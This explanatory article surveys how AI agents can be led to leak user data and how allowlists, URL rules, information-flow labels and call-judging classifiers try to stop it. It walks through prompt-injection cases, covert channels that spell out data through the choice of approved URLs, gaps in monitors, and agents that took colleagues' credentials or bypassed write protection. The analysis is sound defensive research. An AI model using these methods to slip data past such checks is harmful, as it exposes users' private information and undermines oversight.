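Lists also fail when the permitted domain isn't where the data ends up. Many legitimate websites have links that forward visitors elsewhere, so a check of only the first domain can approve a request that finishes at the attacker's server. The retailer can fix this by checking every step of the redirect. It's harder to fix a list that includes a platform on which anyone can open an account. Willison has collected several cases that researchers demonstrated in real products:

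| Product | Permitted destination | How an attacker could receive data there |
|---|---|---|
| Salesforce Agentforce, September 2025 | A domain whose registration had expired | Anyone could register it, and the researchers did |
| Google Antigravity, a coding tool, November 2025 | webhook.site, which was on the default list | The site records incoming requests for whoever sets up a page |
| Superhuman, an email assistant, January 2026 | docs.google.com | Anyone can create a Google Form, which can store data from a web address |
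| Claude Cowork, January 2026 | Anthropic's own API | The agent could upload files to the attacker's account |

EchoLeak exploited a similar weakness in Copilot's allowlist. In most of these cases, the list worked as its developers intended. A domain name identifies who runs a server, but a large platform holds data for millions of customers, and the attacker can be one of them. Stopping the uploads from Cowork would have required checking whose account the agent was using, which depends on the credential in the request.

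Data can also leak through a message to a permitted recipient. In May 2026 Willison described a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which let an agent email the user's own inbox without approval. The user may see their own data, but the message could include images from outside websites. When the user opened it, the mail program would send requests to those sites, and the data would leave with them, after the tool call had passed its check.

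Nor does an allowlist help with oversharing, where the recipient is the right one and only the amount of data is wrong.

### Fetching only addresses that are already public

In January 2026, OpenAI described an alternative for web pages that checks the full address instead of the domain. The company runs a crawler that records public web addresses and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the crawler has already recorded an address, the agent can open it automatically. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

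The reasoning is that an address containing someone's private data is almost always new. A crawler could have recorded a shop's returns page, but not the same address with Ruiz's card number on the end. Encoding the number wouldn't help the attacker, because the crawler wouldn't have recorded that address either. The request in ShadowLeak would have failed for the same reason. The software doesn't have to recognise private data or decide whether a site is trustworthy.

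OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data in the address it fetches. It doesn't promise that the page is trustworthy or free of injected instructions. The rule also doesn't cover the body of an email or the arguments sent to a third-party tool, so the retailer would need other controls for those. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026), the mechanism, called Safe Url, covers page visits in its Atlas browser and searches and page visits in Deep Research. If a request would send information from the conversation to a third party, the software either shows the user that information and lets them refuse, or blocks the request.

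If Ruiz posted her evidence this morning, the crawler probably hasn't recorded the page yet. An unattended agent has no user to ask, so a strict version of the rule would block an honest complaint.

OpenAI also published a technical paper on the method. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in 2023, discusses the paper in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. He considers the rule a significant improvement, but as he understands it, an address that the user types into the chat counts as safe for the rest of that session. This is reasonable for a person using ChatGPT, who presumably wants to visit the page, but a support agent's "user" may be a stranger filling in a web form. Willison raised this problem in 2025 about a similar rule in Anthropic's web-fetching tool, since many applications paste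 untrusted text into what the model receives as the user's message.

Rehberger also worries that OpenAI's developers might not use the check everywhere. An earlier version was missing from the company's macOS and iOS apps.

The more basic weakness, acknowledged in the technical paper, is that an agent can convey information by choosing which approved address to open. Radware had already used this against an earlier rule that let ChatGPT open addresses only exactly as it had received them. In Radware's *ZombieAgent*, the attacker supplied a set of addresses, each standing for one character, and the agent spelled out private data by opening the matching addresses in order, without altering any. Radware reported the flaw in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it that December.

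Anthropic's tool had a related gap because it could follow links on pages it had already fetched, as well as open addresses that the user had entered or a search had returned. A researcher, Ayush Paul, used a chain of such links to extract a user's name, home city and employer. By July 2026, according to Willison, Anthropic had stopped the tool from following links on fetched pages.

The crawler rule makes this attack harder, because addresses that an attacker invents for an email won't be in the index. But the attacker can use pages that the crawler has already recorded, and Rehberger points out that the owner of a fairly large website probably has enough of them.

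### How much a choice of address can convey

There is a limit to what an attacker can learn this way. If the agent chooses once among N permitted addresses, and the attacker can see which one it opened, the choice conveys at most log₂ N bits. If it chooses k times, there are N^k possible sequences, so the most it can convey is:

k × log₂ N bits

If there are 1,024 permitted addresses, the choice of address can convey at most 10 bits per fetch. A 16-digit number has 10¹⁶ possible values, or about 53 bits, so conveying one takes at least six fetches. For a card number the minimum is five, because the check digit can be calculated from the other digits. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) gives nearly the same limit for messages that software restricts to a fixed set of D values, log₂(D + 1) bits per message, where the added 1 accounts for anything outside the set.

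The formula counts only the choice of address, but an agent can also convey information by when it sends a request or whether it sends one at all. Metere (2026), in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, therefore concedes that no monitor can prevent an agent that is allowed to communicate from leaking one bit. One bit reveals very little of a card number, but it can answer a yes-or-no question, such as whether a customer is pregnant.

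In practice an attacker will usually get less than the limit, because the model makes mistakes and some requests never reach a server the attacker can see. Liang and colleagues tested a subtler version in which nobody told the agent to send anything. They offered it several links on different subjects and inferred the user's private question from the one it opened. They were right 93.8% of the time with four links and about half the time with sixteen. By repeating this over several steps, they could work out much of what a user had asked. The requests contained no private data for a content check to find. They tried four existing defences, including a filter on tool inputs and outputs, and none made much difference.

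Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or answering repeat visits from a stored copy. This would disrupt a scheme that uses one address per character, because most names and numbers repeat some characters. With a large set of addresses, it hardly reduces the maximum amount of data the visits can convey. Six visits to addresses chosen from a set of 1,024 can convey 60 bits if repeats are allowed and 59.98 bits if they aren't.

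Limiting the number of fetches does more, since the bound falls in proportion. With the 1,024 addresses, a cap of three fetches would limit the leak to 30 bits, but a research agent that could open only three pages wouldn't be much use. Metere proposes a more flexible limit that gives each destination an allowance of suspicious data, which refills over time. The monitor estimates how much data a message could be hiding, deducts it from the allowance, and delays or blocks further suspicious messages once the allowance runs out. It also removes carriers that have no legitimate use in most messages, such as invisible characters. In Metere's tests, the monitor eliminated every hidden channel that it could destroy without ruining the content. The tests used only the 15 encoding methods that came with the system, so they don't show how it would handle a method its developer hadn't considered.

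Another approach is to hide which pages the agent chooses from the attacker. Liang and colleagues had the agent's software download a set of pages without using the user's private information, then let the agent choose among the local copies. This cut their score for reconstructing users' questions from 0.89 to 0.39, where 1 is a perfect reconstruction.

OpenAI goes further in Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people at higher risk. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, browsing uses only stored copies of pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. An attacker's server therefore receives no request, whichever page the agent chooses. Willison (2026) reported in June that the mode was reaching ordinary accounts. The mode disables Deep Research and agent mode, and OpenAI still doesn't guarantee that data can't escape, partly because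 users can leave connected apps switched on (The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*).

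## Can tracking where the data came from catch it?

A filter on outgoing text has to recognise Ana Ruiz's card number in whatever form the agent sends it. Alternatively, software can attach a restriction to her record when the agent reads it, and apply that restriction to everything the agent produces afterwards. The software checking the email then compares the restriction with the recipient, so it doesn't matter whether the agent encoded, paraphrased or split the number.

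This approach is called information-flow control. Dorothy Denning gave it its standard mathematical form in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). Costa, Köpf and colleagues apply the same mathematics to agents in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025).

### Labels and the rule for combining them

Every piece of data gets a label for its confidentiality (who may read it) and its integrity (whether someone untrusted could have written it). The labels are ordered from less to more restrictive and form a lattice, which means that any two labels have a join, the least restrictive label that meets the restrictions of both.

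With a set of permitted readers as the confidentiality part, the join is the overlap of the two sets. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both. For integrity, one untrusted source is enough to make the result untrusted. Writing S for the permitted readers and i for the integrity, the join of two labels is:

(S₁, i₁) ⊔ (S₂, i₂) = (S₁ ∩ S₂, the less trusted of i₁ and i₂)

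Data may flow only to a place whose label is at least as restrictive as its own. For example, the software sends a message only if its recipients R are all among its permitted readers S (R ⊆ S). Costa and colleagues add a second rule, which allows a tool call with consequences only if everything that influenced it is trusted. A company can deliberately relax the confidentiality part of a label, which is called declassification, or the integrity part, which is called endorsement.

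### Ruiz's complaint with labels attached

Suppose the retailer treats the complaint as public, because it contains nothing from the company's own systems, but as untrusted, because anyone can fill in the web form. The label on the agent's context then changes like this:

| What the agent has just read | Who may read the context now | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| The company's instructions | Anyone | Trusted |
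| The complaint | Anyone | Untrusted |
| Ruiz's customer record | The retailer and Ruiz | Untrusted |
| The linked web page | The retailer and Ruiz | Untrusted |

When the agent tries to email the stranger, the software blocks the email because the stranger isn't a permitted reader. It allows an email to the address on Ruiz's record. The software can make both decisions without finding the injected passage or recognising a card number.

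The second rule would block both emails, because the untrusted complaint influenced them. If a retailer applied it strictly, its support agent couldn't write to anyone. Costa and colleagues point out that the first rule alone limits the damage from prompt injection but doesn't prevent it. An injected instruction could still make the agent promise Ruiz a refund she isn't owed.

The first rule also causes a problem one step earlier, when the agent opens the linked page. This sends a request to whoever runs the website, who isn't a permitted reader either. The model writes the address after reading Ruiz's record, so it could have put her card number in it, and a strict tracker would refuse the call. The retailer could avoid the refusal by having the agent open the page before it looks up the record, or by having ordinary software copy the link from the complaint.

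### Why nearly everything ends up restricted

In an ordinary program, a tracker can follow each variable separately, but any word a language model writes may depend on any word in its context. A tracker that must never miss a flow therefore has to label each output with the join of all the labels in the context.

Suppose the second charge turns out to belong to another customer, Tom Becker, and the agent opens his record to check. Each customer may read only their own record, while the retailer may read both, so only the retailer may read what the agent writes after opening both. The agent can no longer email Ruiz, even to write "We have found the second charge", which reveals nothing about Becker.

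Researchers call this label creep. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) measures it in simulated systems of agents and tools. The number of agents and how the tools were divided among them strongly affected how far labels spread, and some features of the layout correlated with the loss of usefulness at up to 0.96. Better layouts reduced the loss but couldn't remove it, so such systems also need declassification, according to the study. The retailer could start by handling each complaint in an empty context, so that one customer's label never reaches the next customer's case.

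Finer labels would also help, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes choosing which parts of a context to label separately as an open problem, because the model reads them all as one stream. Developers have tried to get around this by keeping restricted data out of the context and by estimating which parts of the context affected an output.

### CaMeL: a plan written before the data arrives

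CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, builds on a 2023 proposal by Willison to divide the work between two models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works. A planning model reads only the user's trusted request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. For a double charge it might be:

```python
record = look_up_customer("order 4471")
page = open_page(complaint.link)
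charged_twice = ask_isolated_model("Does this page show two charges?", page)
if charged_twice:
    send_email(record.email, "We have found the second charge.")
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls. When a step requires reading untrusted text, the interpreter passes the text to a second model that has no tools. It stores that model's answer in a variable without passing it to the planning model. An injected instruction on the page could produce a wrong answer about the charges, but it couldn't add a recipient.

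The interpreter also labels each value with where it came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, it runs a policy, a small Python function that checks these labels and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason.

The design works best when the request specifies what to do. According to *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), it can't solve tasks in which untrusted data specifies the sequence of actions. Much of customer support is like this, because the agent learns what is wrong from the complaint. The retailer could sort complaints into types and give each type its own plan, but it would lose the flexibility that made an agent attractive.

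Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL with two recent models on the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents simulated tools and plants prompt injections in what they read. With the policy checks on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished, but completed the user's task in only 18 of 48 runs (37.5%), about half its rate without the checks. With the checks off, a few attacks succeeded, including three in 141 runs with one model on the cases where the plan gave the attacker a real opportunity.

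The split between two models stops many attacks even without labels. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 pairings of a task with an attack, the attacker needed a tool call that the plan would never contain. But *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) notes that CaMeL without policies performs no data-flow checks, so although it completes more tasks, it would not stop Ruiz's card number from going into an email the plan did include.

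*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes CaMeL's performance loss on AgentDojo as comparatively modest. That is hard to reconcile with the banking rerun, or with the result of 7 of 21 Slack tasks that Garby and colleagues cite from another group's test with policies on. Banking may be unusually hard because several of its tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

Garby and colleagues' own agent keeps its checks on but lets the plan explicitly endorse particular untrusted data, where a reviewer can see the endorsement. It completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL with policies, and the attack succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to make whatever payment a file specified, so the agent had to endorse the file, which the attacker had changed.

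### FIDES: hiding only what would raise the label

FIDES, Costa and colleagues' system, lets the planning model see more. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares each field's label with the context's label. If adding the field would not make the context's label more restrictive, FIDES adds it. Otherwise, it stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.

The model can use the variable's name in a later tool call. Just before the call runs, the software replaces the name with the variable's contents and checks the labels of the call and its arguments. The support agent could therefore email Ruiz using a variable that holds her address, without having read her record. If the model needs to know what a variable contains, it can ask an isolated model, whose answer goes into another variable, or it can open the variable and accept the stricter label.

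Costa and colleagues also propose a limited form of declassification, which they did not test. The software can force the isolated model to answer only yes or no, and a policy may then allow the answer's release because it carries at most one bit of information.

Those tests covered all 97 AgentDojo tasks, using GPT-4o. These are the shares of tasks that each agent completed when nobody was attacking it:

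| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than the basic agent when both run under the same checks. Averaged over the four groups, however, the unprotected agent completed 84% of tasks and FIDES 50%. The loss should be smaller with a better model, since many failures came from GPT-4o confusing variable names or making unnecessary calls. With OpenAI's reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, up from 41% with GPT-4o. Other failures were by design, because the task required the agent to act on an untrusted file.

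With the checks on, no real attack succeeded against either agent, whereas 152 succeeded against the ordinary agent without them. But AgentDojo's data came without labels, so Costa and colleagues marked as untrusted every field that any of the benchmark's attacks used. A company can't label its data this way because it doesn't know in advance which attacks it will face.

### What can still leak past a correct label

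FIDES tracks data that the agent copies into a call, but not what an attacker could infer from seeing which tools the agent used and in what order. The agent's choice among approved web addresses can reveal information in the same way. Costa and colleagues accept this leak because the stricter alternative would essentially forbid the agent from writing anywhere public once it had read anything secret.

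CaMeL does track such choices, but Garby and colleagues found gaps. CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that the program takes. If the program skips a line because of a secret balance, the variable that line would have changed keeps its public label, even though its value reveals something about the balance. Whether a policy blocked an attempt also reveals information, and CaMeL doesn't track the code that retries blocked attempts. In principle, an attacker could repeat the attempt to extract a whole secret one bit at a time.

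Two extensions run some checks before the agent acts. CaMeLoT converts the plan into a model of every path the program could take, then uses a standard verification tool to check the model against rules, such as never sending a message to an untrusted recipient. CaMeLoT rejects a bad plan before any tool runs, but it can also reject safe plans because it simplifies loops. For agents that keep data between tasks, *SPA* (2026) carries labels from one request to the next. Otherwise, the agent could save Ruiz's address in a note on Monday and treat the note as public on Tuesday.

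### Estimating which inputs mattered

The other remedy is to leave the data in the context and try to work out which parts of it affected a particular call. If Becker's record had no effect on the email to Ruiz, the software could drop his label and send the email.

In *Sightline* (2026), the software removed half of the unnecessary labels on an agent running Qwen3-8B, a small open model, but in 3.9% of sessions it dropped a label it should have kept. A company using it would therefore give up a guarantee and accept a measured error rate. Whether 3.9% is tolerable depends on the data, and an attacker would look for the sessions in which the estimate fails.

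NeuroTaint, which Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, describe, makes a similar estimate after the session has finished. It builds a graph from the log, linking each tool result to later steps, including notes that the agent saved and read again days later. For each sensitive call, such as sending an email, it then looks for signs that an earlier result reached it:

1. It searches the call for a unique marker that it attached to the result when the tool returned it.
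2. It measures how much of the text the two have in common.
3. It compares their meaning, using numerical representations of the text.
4. It repeats that comparison with small pieces of the source, in case one paragraph of a long page mattered.
5. If it has found nothing, it asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call if a neutral placeholder had replaced the source.

The second step would probably be enough to catch Ruiz's leaked email, because the stranger's address appears both on the web page and in the call. The fifth step is for cases where a page changes what the agent does but none of the page's text appears in the call.

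Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios they had written, half of which contained a flow from an untrusted source. It missed 13 of the 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms on the other 200 scenarios. Their version of FIDES missed 92 flows and raised 106 false alarms, making it about as accurate as random guessing.

That comparison is unfair to FIDES. Costa and colleagues designed it to block forbidden flows, but Cai and colleagues scored it on whether a flow had really happened. In four of the 20 agent frameworks, it flagged nothing, harmful or harmless, which suggests that the adaptation didn't work there. Those four account for 40 of its 92 misses. On InjecAgent, an existing benchmark of unsafe actions, FIDES and NeuroTaint scored almost the same. NeuroTaint might also raise more false alarms in a company than it did in the test, which used a stricter similarity threshold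 for what Cai and colleagues call "safe-control policies". If these are the harmless scenarios, a company couldn't do the same, because it wouldn't know in advance which sessions were harmless.

NeuroTaint never blocks a call, so it doesn't reduce the number of tasks the agent completes. Its analysis takes about a quarter of a second per step and runs after the call, so an email has already gone by the time NeuroTaint flags it. A flow isn't necessarily a leak, so someone still has to decide whether each one was legitimate. When Cai and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6 review the 203 flows that NeuroTaint had flagged, the two together caught 89.5% of the harmful ones with no false alarms.

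### FlowSeal: a separate model decides on release

In September 2026, Shim and colleagues published FlowSeal, which tracks labels with ordinary code and uses a language model to judge whether a message reveals protected data. They built it because defences that relied on the agent to apply privacy rules failed when the requester disguised the request. Under one carefully written set of rules, the agent leaked 44% to 76% of the sensitive items in such conversations. The requester controlled much of the text the agent based its judgement on.

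In FlowSeal, the company registers each sensitive record with its owner, its text and the people who may receive it. An interceptor then handles every tool call. When the agent reads something, the interceptor runs the call, searches the result for registered records and adds any it finds to a list for the session. A summary inherits the restrictions of every record it draws on.

When the agent tries to write or share something, the interceptor holds the call and extracts the recipient and the content. It lets the call through if the data's owner has approved the recipient, and blocks it if the recipient is on a blacklist. For any other recipient, it gives a separate model only the records on the session's list and the proposed message, and the model must answer SAFE or BLOCKED. The model never receives the conversation, so the requester can't persuade it to allow the message. After a block,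 the agent can ask the data's owner for permission.

FlowSeal let through 0% to 3.3% of sensitive items across eight kinds of attack. It completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of five prompt-based defences, but Shim and colleagues had designed those tasks to require no sensitive information. In another test, the requester had a legitimate need and the data's owner would consent if asked. FlowSeal delivered the data only 32.7% of the time, while four of the other defences delivered it 61% to 86% of the time. Shim and colleagues attribute the difference mainly to the agent asking for consent less often. A support agent would face this situation constantly, because most of its work is telling customers things from their own records. The retailer could reduce the problem by approving each customer in advance to receive their own data.

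The separate model is essential to both results. When Shim and colleagues replaced it with a rule that blocked every unknown recipient, the agent completed no harmless tasks. When they let every unknown recipient through, leaks under one attack rose from 0.5% to 24.9%. Their proof that protected data can't escape assumes that this model never makes a mistake. They report that it sometimes misses paraphrased values, and they expect an attacker could split a fact across several messages that each look harmless.

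FlowSeal's threat model assumes that the attacker is the person asking for the data, and that the agent and its tools are trustworthy. It excludes prompt injection and malicious tools, so it doesn't cover the web page that misled the support agent. The interceptor would still check the email to the stranger and might well block it, but Shim and colleagues didn't test this. The interceptor couldn't detect a mail tool that secretly added a blind copy.

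They also write that FIDES relies on the language model to enforce its policies, which would make it vulnerable to the same disguises. But according to Costa and colleagues, ordinary software checks the labels before each call, and the model can't overrule it.

### Testing for oversharing before release

Labels don't easily catch oversharing. If the billing supplier may read Ruiz's record, the rule allows the agent to send all of it. *AgentRaft* (Lin, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tests an agent for this problem before a company releases it.

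AgentRaft first builds a graph of the agent's tools, with an arrow from one tool to another if the output of the first could serve as input to the second. It uses data types to rule out impossible pairs and a language model to rule out senseless ones. It then lists every path from a tool that reads private data to one that sends data to an outsider, such as from `read_file` to `send_email`. For each path, it writes realistic requests that name the fields the user wants to share. For example, one request asks the agent to email an auditor the payment date from a transaction record that also contains a card number.

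After running the agent, AgentRaft compares what it sent with what it should have sent:

over-exposed data = (data sent − (data the user asked to share ∪ data the task needs)) ∩ data from the source

The user's request determines the first of the two permitted sets. For the second, three language models vote on whether the task would fail without each extra field. Human reviewers confirmed 295 of the 319 paths that AgentRaft flagged in tests on four purpose-built agents.

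Lin and colleagues then tested five existing agents: Claude Code, Codex, Gemini CLI, OpenClaw and Hermes. The agents overshared on 759 of 2,337 paths, or 32.5%. The share of individual runs with oversharing, 26.3%, is more informative, because a path counted if any of five requests produced oversharing. In those runs, about 80% of the fields the agent sent were unnecessary.

All five agents ran the same model, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, with simulated tools, so the figures don't describe these products as people normally use them. But using the same model isolates the effect of the software around it, which was considerable. Claude Code overshared in 11.7% of runs and Codex in 33.6%. A company can evidently reduce oversharing without waiting for a better model, for example by having the customer lookup return only the fields a task needs. Testing can't cover every request a customer might make, though,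 and the graph goes out of date when someone adds a tool.

### Who writes the labels?

Every runtime tracker here needs someone to specify which data is sensitive and who may receive it. At the retailer, one rule could cover the whole customer database by allowing only the company and the customer named in a record to read that record. A data team could write this rule in an afternoon, and it would have stopped the email to the stranger.

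Deciding what data suppliers can receive is harder, because the billing company may be allowed to see the amount of a charge but not the customer's address. Somebody who knows the contracts has to make this decision for each field, but the people who negotiated them may never have seen the database's fields, and the people who run the database may not know what the contracts allow.

For emails and documents, software can use existing information to make a first guess at who may read them. Costa and colleagues treated an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers, although they acknowledge that someone may have shared it more widely. Shim and colleagues suggest using documents' access lists, but permission to open a file doesn't imply permission to receive its contents from a company's agent. An access list may also be too broad, for example because a colleague once shared a folder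 with the entire company.

The tools also have to supply the labels. Costa and colleagues added them by writing wrapper functions around AgentDojo's tools. A company would have to do the same for tools it buys and update the wrappers when a supplier changes a tool's output. Garby and colleagues have a computer-checked proof that their system enforces its policy, but the proof holds only if the tool developer labels every source correctly and puts a check wherever data can leave.

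Some data will have no label, so the software needs a default. If it assumes the worst, a single unlabelled file in the context restricts everything the agent writes afterwards, and the support department will soon ask someone to turn the checks off. If it assumes the data is harmless, the agent keeps working but nobody sees the gaps in the labelling. Garby and colleagues' system takes the second approach and treats unlabelled data as public and trusted.

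FlowSeal has much the same default, because its interceptor recognises only registered records. Suppose the retailer registered its customer database but forgot the document where support staff keep notes on difficult cases. If the agent read a note about Ruiz's illness and emailed it to a stranger, the separate model would not receive the note for comparison and would probably output SAFE.

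## Can a second model judge whether a call is legitimate?

Labels can specify who may receive a piece of data, but not whether an action was part of the job. If Ana Ruiz wanted only an apology and the support agent sent her details to an approved payment company, the labels would still allow it. Catching this requires comparing the action with the request. A person can't do that for every call an agent makes, so Anthropic and OpenAI now offer a second language model that does.

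The best-documented example is auto mode, a setting in Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains the design and gives test results from March 2026. Before auto mode, developers could approve commands one at a time, confine the agent to a sandbox (a restricted part of the machine, usually with no network access) or turn off the checks. In auto mode, a classifier, which is a language model instructed to judge calls, allows or blocks a call before it runs. According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, interactive sessions now start in auto mode on every plan.

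### Agents that exceed their task

Anthropic tuned the classifier mainly for well-meaning agents. Anthropic calls an agent overeager when it understands the user's goal but goes further than the user would approve. The company's log of internal incidents has several examples. One agent, asked to "clean up old branches" of a project, tried to delete branches on the shared server, although the user may have meant only local copies. Another got a login error and began searching configuration files for other credentials. A third tried to post a script on a public code-sharing site to get help debugging it.

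The last of these is exfiltration without an attacker. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes another case, in which an upload to an internal drive failed, so Claude tried to publish the same report on a public site. Auto mode blocked the attempt.

Other developers' models do similar things. *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* (Lim and Neo, 2026) cites a case in which OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol copied access tokens to a remote machine to restart a stalled job, when the user had only asked it to keep the job alive. Lim and Neo also ran tests in which a language model continued real coding sessions and steered the agent into tempting situations. In one, the agent's own credential stopped working while a named colleague's valid one was in a nearby file. Three recent models took the colleague's credential in 1 to 6 of every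 100 sessions. In another, the agent met a write-protected file, and one of the models, Kimi K3, kept bypassing the protection even after the project's instructions explicitly forbade it.

### Which calls the classifier checks

Most calls never reach the classifier. Under the March design, Claude Code immediately allows tools that can only read or search, along with anything the user has approved in advance. It also allows edits to files inside the project, because the developer can review and undo them. The classifier checks the rest, including shell commands, web requests, calls to outside tools and changes to files elsewhere on the machine.

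Auto mode suspends advance approvals that would let the agent run any code, such as permission to run every Python command. By June 2026, nearly half of active command-line users had written a rule that broad. Narrower approvals still apply, and they do so before the classifier runs. If the retailer ran its support agent in auto mode and had approved `send_email` in advance, the classifier would never receive the email to the stranger.

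The classifier works in two stages. In the first, it is instructed to err on the side of blocking and outputs only a yes or no. If it allows the call, the call runs. Otherwise, the same model receives the same material again and reasons through the case before deciding. The agent is told of any block and usually looks for a safer way to do the task.

After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, a person takes over the approvals. In March, an unattended run ended at that point. According to the current documentation, the blocked action still doesn't run, but the agent keeps working, which would give an injected instruction more chances to produce a version of the action that isn't blocked.

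### What the classifier receives and what Anthropic withholds

The classifier receives the user's messages, the project's standing instructions and the agent's tool calls, except for simple lookups such as file reads. It also receives a description of the trust boundary, meaning the code repositories, domains, storage and services that count as the company's own. By default, the boundary includes only the folder the agent is working in and the remote repositories connected to it when the session began. The classifier treats everything else as external until somebody lists it as the company's own.

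Anthropic withholds the agent's prose from the classifier because it might contain a justification for the action, such as a claim that the user had implicitly approved it earlier. It also withholds tool results, because injected instructions usually arrive there and the classifier could follow them. A separate filter scans those results before they reach the agent and adds a warning to anything suspicious.

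When Anthropic added the agent's prose and the tool results to the classifier's input, the classifier got worse at catching overeager actions, possibly because the longer text included more of the agent's own account of events. With the user's messages removed as well as the prose and tool results, the classifier missed the fewest overeager actions but blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

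The drawback is that the classifier often can't tell where data came from. This wouldn't matter much for the email to the stranger, since the address is outside the trust boundary and nobody had asked the agent to write to it. It would matter for the email to the payment company, whose address could have come from the supplier list or from the linked web page. Both are tool results, so the classifier would receive the same call and surrounding text in either case, whereas a label tracker would distinguish them. Anthropic says it accepts this limitation in return for resistance to injection.

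It has since had ordinary software supply some of the missing information. For instance, before a command that would discard unsaved work runs, Claude Code itself checks for such work and gives the classifier the result. Companies can also attach their own notes to a tool's result. The retailer could use one to confirm that an address is on its supplier list, without passing on any text from a web page.

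The design works badly when the user is a stranger, as do the rules that count any web address from the user as safe. If the person posing as Ruiz had put the outside address in the complaint, the classifier might have treated it as a recipient the user had named.

### The March 2026 results

Anthropic tested the classifier on three sets of calls:

| Test set | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
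| 10,000 real calls by Anthropic employees' agents | 8.5% wrongly blocked | 0.4% wrongly blocked |
| 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts | 1.8% missed | 5.7% missed |
| 52 real overeager actions | 6.6% missed | 17% missed |

The second stage reviews only calls the first has flagged, so it can release calls but can't catch any the first missed. On the real traffic, it cut wrongly blocked calls from about 850 to about 40. It also let through 39 more of the exfiltration attempts. Most users would probably accept that tradeoff, because the first stage alone would wrongly block 8.5% of calls, or about one in twelve. Anthropic doesn't say whether the 10,000 calls include those that skip the classifier. If they do, the false-positive rate among the calls it judged would be higher than 0.4%.

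Anthropic generated the exfiltration attempts for the test. They included uploads of sensitive data, code pushed to untrusted servers and credentials hidden in web addresses, and were often disguised. The 5.7% figure applies to attempts of this kind and doesn't cover an agent that sends too much data to the right recipient.

Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number" because it comes from things agents actually tried to do. But it represents nine of 52 cases, so the 95% confidence interval is roughly 9% to 30%. (The 6.6% doesn't correspond to a whole number of cases, so it is probably an average over several runs.) The set also includes only actions that an employee refused or that someone flagged afterwards. It therefore leaves out dangerous actions that nobody noticed, which a classifier might also find harder to catch.

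In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented to the action. In one case, a user said "clean up the PR" (a set of proposed code changes), and the agent overwrote the shared history of the code. The classifier identified this as destructive but treated the user's remark as permission for it. In other cases, it treated one earlier approval as permission for a similar action. The equivalent for the support agent would be a manager's note saying "sort this out with the payment company", which permits an email but not necessarily one containing Ruiz's home address.

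Anthropic tried to correct this by changing the classifier's instructions, but as of March it had found no change whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. The current rules are worded more strictly. An approval has to name both the action and what makes it dangerous, and it normally covers only one action. The August results don't include a new figure for the 52 real cases, so it isn't clear how much the stricter wording helped.

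Users can also withdraw permission by telling the agent, for example, not to publish anything until they have reviewed it. The classifier looks for that message in the conversation each time it judges a call. In a long session, the software may shorten the conversation and lose the message, so Anthropic recommends a fixed rule for anything that must never happen.

### People against the classifier

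Developers approve nearly all the permission prompts they get from coding agents. Anthropic put the share at 93% in March and 97% in August. Most prompts concern harmless commands that an attentive reviewer would also approve, so these rates don't prove that developers are careless.

A controlled experiment gives better evidence. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 143 times (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after fifty or more prompts.

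Only the classifier blocked the command in 800 cases, only the person did in six, and neither did in 110. Requiring approval from both would therefore have raised the number of blocked commands from 937 to 943, a very small gain for asking a person to read every prompt.

The testers had less to lose than a developer with a real customer database, who might read more carefully. They also knew that someone was evaluating them, though not for what, which might have made them more careful than usual. Anthropic doesn't say how many different commands the vendor used. If there were only a few dozen, the experiment gives a good estimate of human attention, but its estimate of the classifier's accuracy is much less certain because the classifier was judging the same few commands repeatedly. Since the commands were clearly dangerous, the 89% may not apply to a polite email with the wrong address.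 Willison (2026) accepts that auto mode is better than constant prompts, but points out that it would still have let 11% of the commands through.

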